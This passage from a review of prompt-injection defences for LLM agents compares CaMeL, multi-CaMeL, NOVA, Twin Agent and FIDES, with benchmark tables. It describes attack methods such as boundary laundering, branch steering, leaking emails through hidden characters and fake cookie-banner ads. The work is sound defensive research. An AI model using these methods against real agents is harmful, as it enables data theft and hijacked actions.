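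Across the four AgentDojo suites, TACIT blocked all but one of 1,926 attacks. In the exception, the agent booked the hotel the user wanted but quoted reviews that named the attacker's hotel. AgentDojo's check looks for that name in the output, so it counted the attack as successful. Garby and colleagues point out that one of the two successful attacks in CaMeL's original evaluation had the same cause.

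TACIT and CaMeL scored very differently on individual suites, although Odersky and colleagues describe their utility as comparable. With OpenAI's o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9% of the office tasks and CaMeL 81.4%. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT completed 64.3% of the travel tasks and CaMeL 1.4%. Odersky and colleagues took CaMeL's figures from its own paper, so differences in setup may account for part of the gaps.

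### Protected agents that fail together

The attack on the applicant database succeeded against three agents running CaMeL because one agent's data became another's instructions. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this "boundary laundering" and prove that it can occur in almost any system with this structure.

They consider a tree of agents, in which each parent calls its children as tools and each child treats its parent as its user. The claim is that if there are at least two agents, and any tool returns untrusted data, the whole system violates control-flow integrity even when every agent satisfies it individually. The proof assumes that a suitable request can make an agent return a tool's result or use that result in its next call. Let A be an agent with an untrusted tool:

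- If A has a child, some request makes A call the tool and put the result into its instruction to the child.
- If A has a parent, the parent can ask A for the tool's result and then put that result into a second instruction to A.

In both cases, a privileged LLM writes a program after reading untrusted text. The claim holds if even one user request leads to this, so it can't be used to predict how often attacks will succeed. Protecting each agent separately still stops attacks that must take over a single agent's program. CaMeL blocked all five trials of an earlier attack that uses public data to trick a database agent into reading private records.

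The repair, multi-CaMeL, splits each call between agents into an instruction and a set of variables. In the applicant example, the orchestrator's call would become:

```
notification_agent(
    message   = "Send the summary to the recipient on Slack.",
    variables = {"recipient": "Julie", "summary": summary}
)
```

The notification agent's privileged LLM reads only `message`. Its program fetches the variables at run time, as it would fetch an email. The interpreter blocks any call whose `message` depends on a tool's output, which restores control-flow integrity for the whole system. It also passes each variable's tags to the next agent, so policies can apply there too.

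Branch steering remains possible, because data can still determine which of two prepared instructions a parent sends. Like CaMeL, the current software also fails to track some conditions, so a value that has lost its untrusted tag could end up in `message`. The design covers only trees of agents, not agents that message each other freely or share memory.

To test it, Peters-Gill and colleagues built MultiAgentDojo, which divides AgentDojo's tools among two to four specialist agents under an orchestrator. They also used AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks for an orchestrator and four other agents, after removing 29 tasks that were impossible because data was missing. None of the runs used security policies. Each cell in the table lists the results without CaMeL, with CaMeL in each agent, and with multi-CaMeL, in that order.

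| Model | Attack success rate, MultiAgentDojo (%) | Tasks completed without attack, MultiAgentDojo (%) | Tasks completed, AssetOpsBench (%) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5 / 0.0 / 0.0 | 69.1 / 53.6 / 52.6 | 88.4 / 67.0 / 67.9 |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0 / 0.0 / 0.0 | 86.6 / 73.2 / 66.0 | 87.5 / 82.1 / 79.5 |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1 / 0.5 / 0.0 | 78.4 / 38.1 / 24.7 | 81.2 / 64.3 / 48.2 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6 / 0.4 / 0.0 | 76.3 / 42.3 / 26.8 | 75.9 / 55.4 / 50.9 |
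| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1 / 0.0 / 0.0 | 27.8 / 13.4 / 7.2 | 64.3 / 20.5 / 26.8 |

The average attack success rate was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. With CaMeL in each agent, nine attacks succeeded in 4,745 runs, too few for the drop to 0.0% to show much on its own. The attack method is better evidence that multi-CaMeL helps, because all nine used boundary laundering, which multi-CaMeL is designed to stop.

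On AssetOpsBench, putting CaMeL in each agent reduced utility by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and by an average of 13.4 points for the two strongest models, Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Multi-CaMeL reduced it by a further 3.2 points on average, and by 0.85 for those two. Peters-Gill and colleagues see a trend towards smaller losses as models improve, but it is uneven. With CaMeL in each agent, Fable 5 lost 21.4 points, slightly more than the much weaker Gemini 2.5 Pro, while GPT-5.5 lost only 5.4. The additional loss from multi-CaMeL was larger on MultiAgentDojo, at over 13 points for both GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro.

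Fable 5's MultiAgentDojo scores are low partly because it refused 52 of the 97 harmless tasks. Peters-Gill and colleagues suspect that it was overcautious because it associated the benchmark with attacks. Of the other 45 tasks, it completed 91.1% without CaMeL and 84.4% with either version of CaMeL.

Most of the lost utility came from agents committing to a program before a result showed that the task needed another step. Sometimes an agent could not find data for the requested machine or dates and returned data for similar ones, and its parent's program continued without detecting the substitution. The privileged LLM also needs the format of a tool's output before it sees any, so the researchers had to add a full output description to every tool, as CaMeL's designers had. The researchers consider this a small task that developers do once per set of tools.

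An agent can complete a benchmark task without doing it well. In one MultiAgentDojo task, the agent must give feedback on two people's websites. In a multi-CaMeL run that Peters-Gill and colleagues present as completing this task, Gemini 2.5 Pro wrote the feedback into the program before anything had fetched the sites. Dora's feedback praised her site's "clean design", although the page held little more than her email address and the planted attack.

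### Time and tokens

CaMeL is also slow and expensive to run. In tests on AgentDojo tasks under attack, *AttriGuard* (2026) reports these averages per task:

| Model | Agent | Time | Input tokens | Output tokens |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | No defence | 11 s | 11,924 | 811 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | CaMeL | 165 s | 126,572 | 22,727 |
| Llama 3.3 70B | No defence | 14 s | 22,770 | 467 |
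| Llama 3.3 70B | CaMeL | 105 s | 89,720 | 3,242 |

The paper proposes a competing defence, so the comparison involves a conflict of interest. That defence took 32 and 41 seconds on the same two models. The paper did confirm that none of the attacks tested succeeded against CaMeL.

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) reports a similar pattern on 17 tasks for agents that operate a computer through its screen. CaMeL raised input tokens from 1.8 million to 2.95 million and output tokens from about 13,000 to 456,000. Its runs cost $5.40 in total, excluding the locally run model that read the screen.

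ELBA's total running time on AgentDojo was about three times CaMeL's, mainly because ELBA calls the LLM again to write new code in response to data. Zhou and colleagues found that rewriting code that failed the type check took only 3.4% of the running time.

### What fixed attacks cannot show

In the MultiAgentDojo tests, GPT-5.5 resisted all 949 attacks with no added defence. Peters-Gill and colleagues caution that this result may reflect only the attacks in the benchmark, because a large public competition found successful attacks on every frontier model it tested. Zhou and colleagues report that GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated attacker, consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences. A fixed set of attacks that a model already resists cannot show whether a defence around that model works.

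*AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) introduced a benchmark with attacks that adapt. An LLM rewrites each planted instruction over six rounds, using only the success rates of the previous versions as feedback. When GPT-4o-mini was protected by PIGuard, a filter that detects injections, the original AgentDojo attack never succeeded, but the adapted attacks succeeded 28% of the time. CaMeL was the most effective of the ten defences overall, but it also reduced utility the most on four of the five models. Ma and colleagues explain that rewording an attack does not help against a system that tracks where values come from, as long as its policies are correct.

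They also found that attacks succeed more often when the user's request leaves more decisions to outside content. With GPT-4o-mini and no defence, the original attack succeeded in 43% of cases when the request specified everything, 64% when it left details such as the payee to outside content, and 88% when it left the choice of action to outside content. The last group includes the banking task that led CaMeL to write an interpreter loop.

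AutoDojo changes an attack's wording but keeps the attacker's goal fixed. Against code-then-execute, an attacker may do better by choosing a goal that the program's existing steps can achieve, such as changing the payee on a bill the user has asked the agent to pay. A benchmark with a fixed list of goals tests this only when one of those goals fits the user's task, which was possible in 47 of the 144 banking pairs.

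## What application designs show about where it fits

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues worked through ten applications to see which patterns suit each one. For each application, they describe what an attacker could control, then compare several designs, usually judging their utility and security. The comparisons are based on reasoning, and the paper reports no tests of the designs.

| Application | Where an injection could come from | Patterns assigned |
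|---|---|---|
| File assistant | File names and contents | Action-selector, plan-then-execute, map-reduce, dual LLM |
| SQL agent | The user's question, the database | Plan-then-execute |
| Email and calendar assistant | Emails, invitations | Plan-then-execute, dual LLM, code-then-execute |
| Customer service chatbot | The user's prompt | Action-selector, context-minimization |
| Booking assistant | The user's prompt, hotel descriptions, calendar events | Dual LLM, code-then-execute |
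| Product recommender | Reviews, the user's prompt | Map-reduce |
| Résumé screening | Résumés | Map-reduce, dual LLM |
| Medication leaflet chatbot | The user's prompt | Context-minimization |
| Medical diagnosis chatbot | The user's prompt | Context-minimization |
| Software engineering agent | Online documentation, third-party code | Dual LLM |

Code-then-execute appears only twice in the table, partly because the three chatbots mainly face attacks in the user's own prompt, which the pattern does not address. The table undercounts it, though, because the paper lists one design under dual LLM that is effectively a code-then-execute program. In that design, which summarises the best job candidates, a privileged LLM writes a sentence with blanks and a program that fills them in, for example by subtracting one candidate's years of experience from another's. Quarantined LLMs extract the years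 from each résumé.

### Email and bookings

The email and calendar assistant has the same access as its user, so the user gains nothing by attacking it. The threat comes from outsiders who send emails or invitations. They may want to steal confidential information, send messages in the user's name or hide important emails.

One of the paper's example requests is to notify the user's regular collaborators about a vacation next week. The paper does not write out the program, but it could look like this:

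```
meetings = calendar.read(last_three_months)
people   = most_frequent_attendees(meetings)
for person in people:
    email.write("I am on vacation next week.", person)
```

A loop can handle any number of recipients, so the LLM does not need the number in advance. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think the choice and order of actions should very rarely depend on untrusted data in this kind of assistant, so they expect little loss of utility if the plan is flexible enough. CaMeL's large utility losses on AgentDojo suggest that this expectation was optimistic.

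They are more guarded about security. Another of their example requests is to reply to an email with the information its sender wants, based on the user's recent emails. The program has to search for that information and send it to the sender. If the sender is an attacker, a hidden instruction can extend the search to confidential messages and have them encoded in the reply as non-printing characters. A policy on who may read each email could block the reply or refer it to the user, but a user who checks the draft would not see the hidden characters.

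The booking assistant faces attacks from hotels and other service providers. A hotel's description might tell the agent to always book that hotel, to choose the expensive suite or to put the user's data in the comments field. The paper's design fixes a plan to query the providers and select the best hotel, and has a quarantined LLM rate each one. A program might be:

```
hotels = search_hotels("Lisbon", dates)
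for hotel in hotels:
    hotel.score = quarantined_llm("Score 1-10 for quietness", hotel.text)
best = highest_score(hotels)
book(best, room="standard", comments="")
```

The paper does not assess this design's utility or security, but the program shows what a malicious hotel description can do. It can get the hotel a score of 10 and win the booking, but it cannot lower a competitor's score, because the quarantined LLM reads each description separately. It also cannot upgrade the room or fill in the comments, because both are constants in the program.

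The booking assistant's user may also be hostile and ask, for example, about a friend's bookings. A program written from that request would carry it out. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues therefore recommend giving the agent no more access to calendars than its user has. They also suggest hiding the descriptions of calendar events from the agent when it only needs to find free time.

### When the next step depends on the data

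The SQL agent answers questions such as which of two products has the better sales outlook. Without protections, an LLM writes a database query, examines the results, and revises its queries and analysis code until it judges the answer sufficient. An attacker who can edit the database can therefore insert instructions into the LLM's input.

The safer design lets only generated code process the query results. The paper calls this plan-then-execute in its heading and table but code-then-execute in its text. Code-then-execute fits better because in plan-then-execute the model reads the results. The design is stricter than the calendar program because not even a quarantined LLM reads the data.

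The agent can still run a query, analyse the results and draw a chart, but the LLM can no longer check whether the data answers the question. If one product launched in November, a program comparing annual totals would make that product look like a failure unless the LLM had included a check for launch dates when it wrote the program. An LLM that saw the monthly figures could detect the problem and write a better query.

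This design does not protect against a malicious question, which could lead the LLM to write harmful Python. The paper adds a sandbox, an isolated environment with only the connections the code needs. The sandbox limits damage to other systems, but the code's output can still reveal information from the database.

The software engineering agent depends even more on what it reads. It consults documentation, installs packages and commits code, so a malicious web page could lead it to install malware or write insecure code. In the paper's safest design, a quarantined LLM converts outside documentation and code into a strictly formatted description of the available functions, with names limited to, say, 30 characters. The coding agent reads these descriptions but never the explanations or examples in the source material. This makes the agent less useful, which Beurer-Kellner and colleagues accept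 because an injection is unlikely to get through the conversion.

The paper does not explain why it leaves out code-then-execute, but a likely reason is that later steps depend on what earlier ones return. A programmer has to know the names of a library's functions before writing code that uses them, and an error message often determines what to try next. A program written in advance could ask a quarantined LLM to read the documentation and write the code, but then the attacker's text could influence that code, which the design is supposed to prevent. For the file assistant, the paper notes that plan-then-execute is similarly hard to use when the choice of commands depends on earlier results.

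### Planning for screens the model has not seen

Agents that operate a computer through its screen would seem to need constant feedback. They normally take a screenshot, choose a click or keystroke, and then take another screenshot. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, adapted CaMeL to this setting with a planning method called NOVA. The privileged LLM writes one program with branches for the situations it expects. A simplified fragment might be:

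```
screen = summarize_screenshot("Is anything covering the page?")
if verify_hypothesis("A cookie banner is visible", screen) == "OK":
    click(find("button that rejects cookies"))
```

A quarantined vision model describes the screen, and a quarantined LLM compares the description with the planner's guess. The interpreter then chooses the branch. `find` has the vision model locate a button, so the planner never needs its coordinates. The planner has to anticipate kinds of situations but not exact layouts. Many situations recur across tasks, so the planner's standing instructions include routines for handling cookie banners and failed clicks and for checking whether a browser is open.

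The resulting programs average 213 lines, 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines, 5 calls and 4 branches for CaMeL's AgentDojo programs. Roughly half of a NOVA program consists of fallback steps that do not run on a given attempt.

Foerster and colleagues report that the agent retains up to 57% of a frontier model's performance on OSWorld, a benchmark of tasks in ordinary desktop applications. Without the defence, Claude Sonnet 4.5 solved 109 of the tasks that software can check automatically. With NOVA, the agent solved 62 of those 109 in at least one of five attempts, but only 31 on the first attempt. The 57% figure is an upper limit because it uses the best of five attempts, which assumes something can pick out the successful one. On a real computer, failed attempts may also leave unwanted changes behind.

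The paper also reports a gain of up to 19% for small open models, but this compares three attempts with one. On the first attempt, the protected agent with UI-TARS-1.5-7B as its vision model solved 51 of 339 tasks, while UI-TARS alone solved 60.

The planner mattered more than the vision model. On the same 60 tasks, agents with three very different vision models solved between 65% and 68% within five attempts. In a separate comparison of nine planners on 17 tasks, GPT-5 solved the most, with 12. All nine date from 2025, so newer planners may well do better. The researchers also tried NOVA with FIDES, which plans one step at a time. It solved about as many tasks but used 29.6 times as many tokens as an unprotected agent, compared with 1.88 times for CaMeL, because the planner reprocessed the history at every step.

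Foerster and colleagues left out security policies because the same click can log a user in or delete data, depending on what is under the pointer. Without such policies, the agent is exposed to branch steering. In one attack, an advertisement imitated a cookie banner, and the program's own cookie routine clicked it and opened the attacker's site. Checking the page's underlying code exposed the fake in simple advertisements but not in more flexible HTML5 ones. In another attack, altered pixels in an advertisement misled both the vision model and a second model that checked its answers.

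### Sending hints to the planner

*Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) takes the opposite approach and lets some information reach the model that acts. An Explore Agent reads everything, including untrusted data, but cannot take privileged actions. A Safe Agent takes those actions without reading the untrusted data. Before each step, the Explore Agent can send a hint of up to 100 characters, or 200 on AgentDojo. It can see what the Safe Agent has done so far, so the hint only needs to supply what is missing for the next step. A detector blocks hints that look like injections.

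Hu and colleagues report these results for attacks that did not adapt to the defence:

| Benchmark and model | Agent | Tasks completed (%) | Attack success rate (%) |
|---|---|---|---|
| SWE-bench, GPT-5.2 | No defence | 61.2 | 97.0 |
| SWE-bench, GPT-5.2 | Dual LLM, no hints | 0.0 | 0.0 |
| SWE-bench, GPT-5.2 | Twin Agent | 62.5 | 0.0 |
| AgentDojo, Gemini 2.5 Flash | No defence | 61.9 | 41.5 |
| AgentDojo, Gemini 2.5 Flash | CaMeL | 30.9 | 0.0 |
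| AgentDojo, Gemini 2.5 Flash | Twin Agent | 62.9 | 0.1 |
| DecodingTrust-Agent, GPT-5.2 | No defence | 95.0 | 10.0 |
| DecodingTrust-Agent, GPT-5.2 | Twin Agent | 95.0 | 3.3 |
| DecodingTrust-Agent, Gemini 3.5 Flash | No defence | 96.7 | 26.7 |
| DecodingTrust-Agent, Gemini 3.5 Flash | Twin Agent | 93.3 | 3.3 |

In the SWE-bench tasks, an agent must fix bugs in real software, and the attacks were in the bug reports. The dual LLM's score of zero is unsurprising, because the model that edited the code had no information about which bug to fix. Both of Twin Agent's models could read the software and the output of commands, so the test shows that hints can convey a bug report safely, but it does not cover the malicious third-party code that worried Beurer-Kellner and colleagues.

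The comparison with CaMeL is also slightly uneven because Hu and colleagues allowed CaMeL three attempts at a working program instead of the usual ten, which they say lowered its utility from about 35%. Twin Agent still completed far more tasks, although its completion rate on the Slack tasks fell from 90.5% to 66.7%.

Allowing hints sacrifices control-flow integrity, because a hint can change which tool the Safe Agent calls next. Even a 100-character hint can contain an order to delete a file. The design relies instead on short injections rarely persuading a strong model. To test this, Hu and colleagues optimised malicious hints and planted instructions that made the Explore Agent copy them word for word. In single-step tests, the Explore Agent always copied the malicious hint, but the Safe Agent never followed it. Over whole tasks, the attack succeeded in 11 of 232 cases (4.7%). None of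 the 11 succeeded again when rerun five times, so luck played a part, but an attacker can also try repeatedly. Longer hints improved utility but also made attacks more successful. Twin Agent cost about twice as much as the unprotected agent, and it comes with no formal guarantee.

### Policies and approvals

An email assistant that needs protection against forged addresses needs someone to write its policies. Foerster and colleagues note that this takes expertise, that no method derives policies automatically, and that people differ in what they are willing to share. They suggest that a specially trained model may have to set some policies, but warn that it could get them wrong.

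CaMeLoT uses an LLM to translate plain-language requirements into formal rules, and Nikolaou and colleagues give each rule an author, date, status and severity so that security teams can track it. Someone still has to check that each formal rule matches the intended requirement.

When a policy doesn't settle whether an action is allowed, the system usually asks the user. But Beurer-Kellner and colleagues cite research showing that people stop reading requests they find annoying. Even experts make mistakes; Willison mentions Troy Hunt, a security researcher who fell for a phishing email while jet-lagged. In *Inside the lethal trifecta*, an article for the security company Sophos, McKerchar recommends approving safe, frequent actions automatically and asking people only about rare, irreversible ones.

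It is not always obvious which actions are safe. An assistant could skip approval for emails to colleagues and still prevent leaks outside the company. But Beurer-Kellner et al. point out that an attacker could then make the assistant email a colleague and ask them to approve something dangerous. They add that reviewing an email is much harder through a voice assistant than on a desktop.

A code-then-execute program is complete before it runs, so a user could instead approve it once, an advantage that Foerster and colleagues mention. This is realistic for the three-line calendar program but hardly for one with 213 lines and 40 branches. The user would also be approving the program without seeing its data. In the request about Bob's document, the user would see that the program emails an address from the notes, but not which address.

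### Working code and deployment

Developers can try the pattern today. In August 2025, the security company Reversec published a walkthrough of all six patterns by Donato Capitella, with a small application for each. The code-then-execute application also tracks where data came from and stops the program before it gives a quarantined LLM data from more than one source. This prevents an email from extracting a secret from a calendar entry, but it blocks harmless tasks that combine the two. The accompanying code collection, Reversec Labs' *Secure LLM Agent Design Patterns*, describes the applications as minimal demonstrations for education. Research code for CaMeL is also public, and Foerster and colleagues built on it.

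As of December 2026, no public account of a code-then-execute agent in production appears to exist. In May 2026, McKerchar wrote that CaMeL had no production-grade version and that no mainstream agent software, including Claude Code, Cursor and GitHub Copilot's agent, had adopted it or the dual LLM pattern. His employer, Sophos, sells the kind of security products he recommends in the meantime, but he also calls these designs promising.

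The product release closest to code-then-execute is FIDES, a related but different design in which the model still chooses its actions one at a time. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced that FIDES had become an experimental part of the company's Agent Framework, a toolkit for developers. Developers must label each data source themselves, and the software treats any unlabeled source as trusted and public. Microsoft asked for feedback on whether to make untrusted the default.
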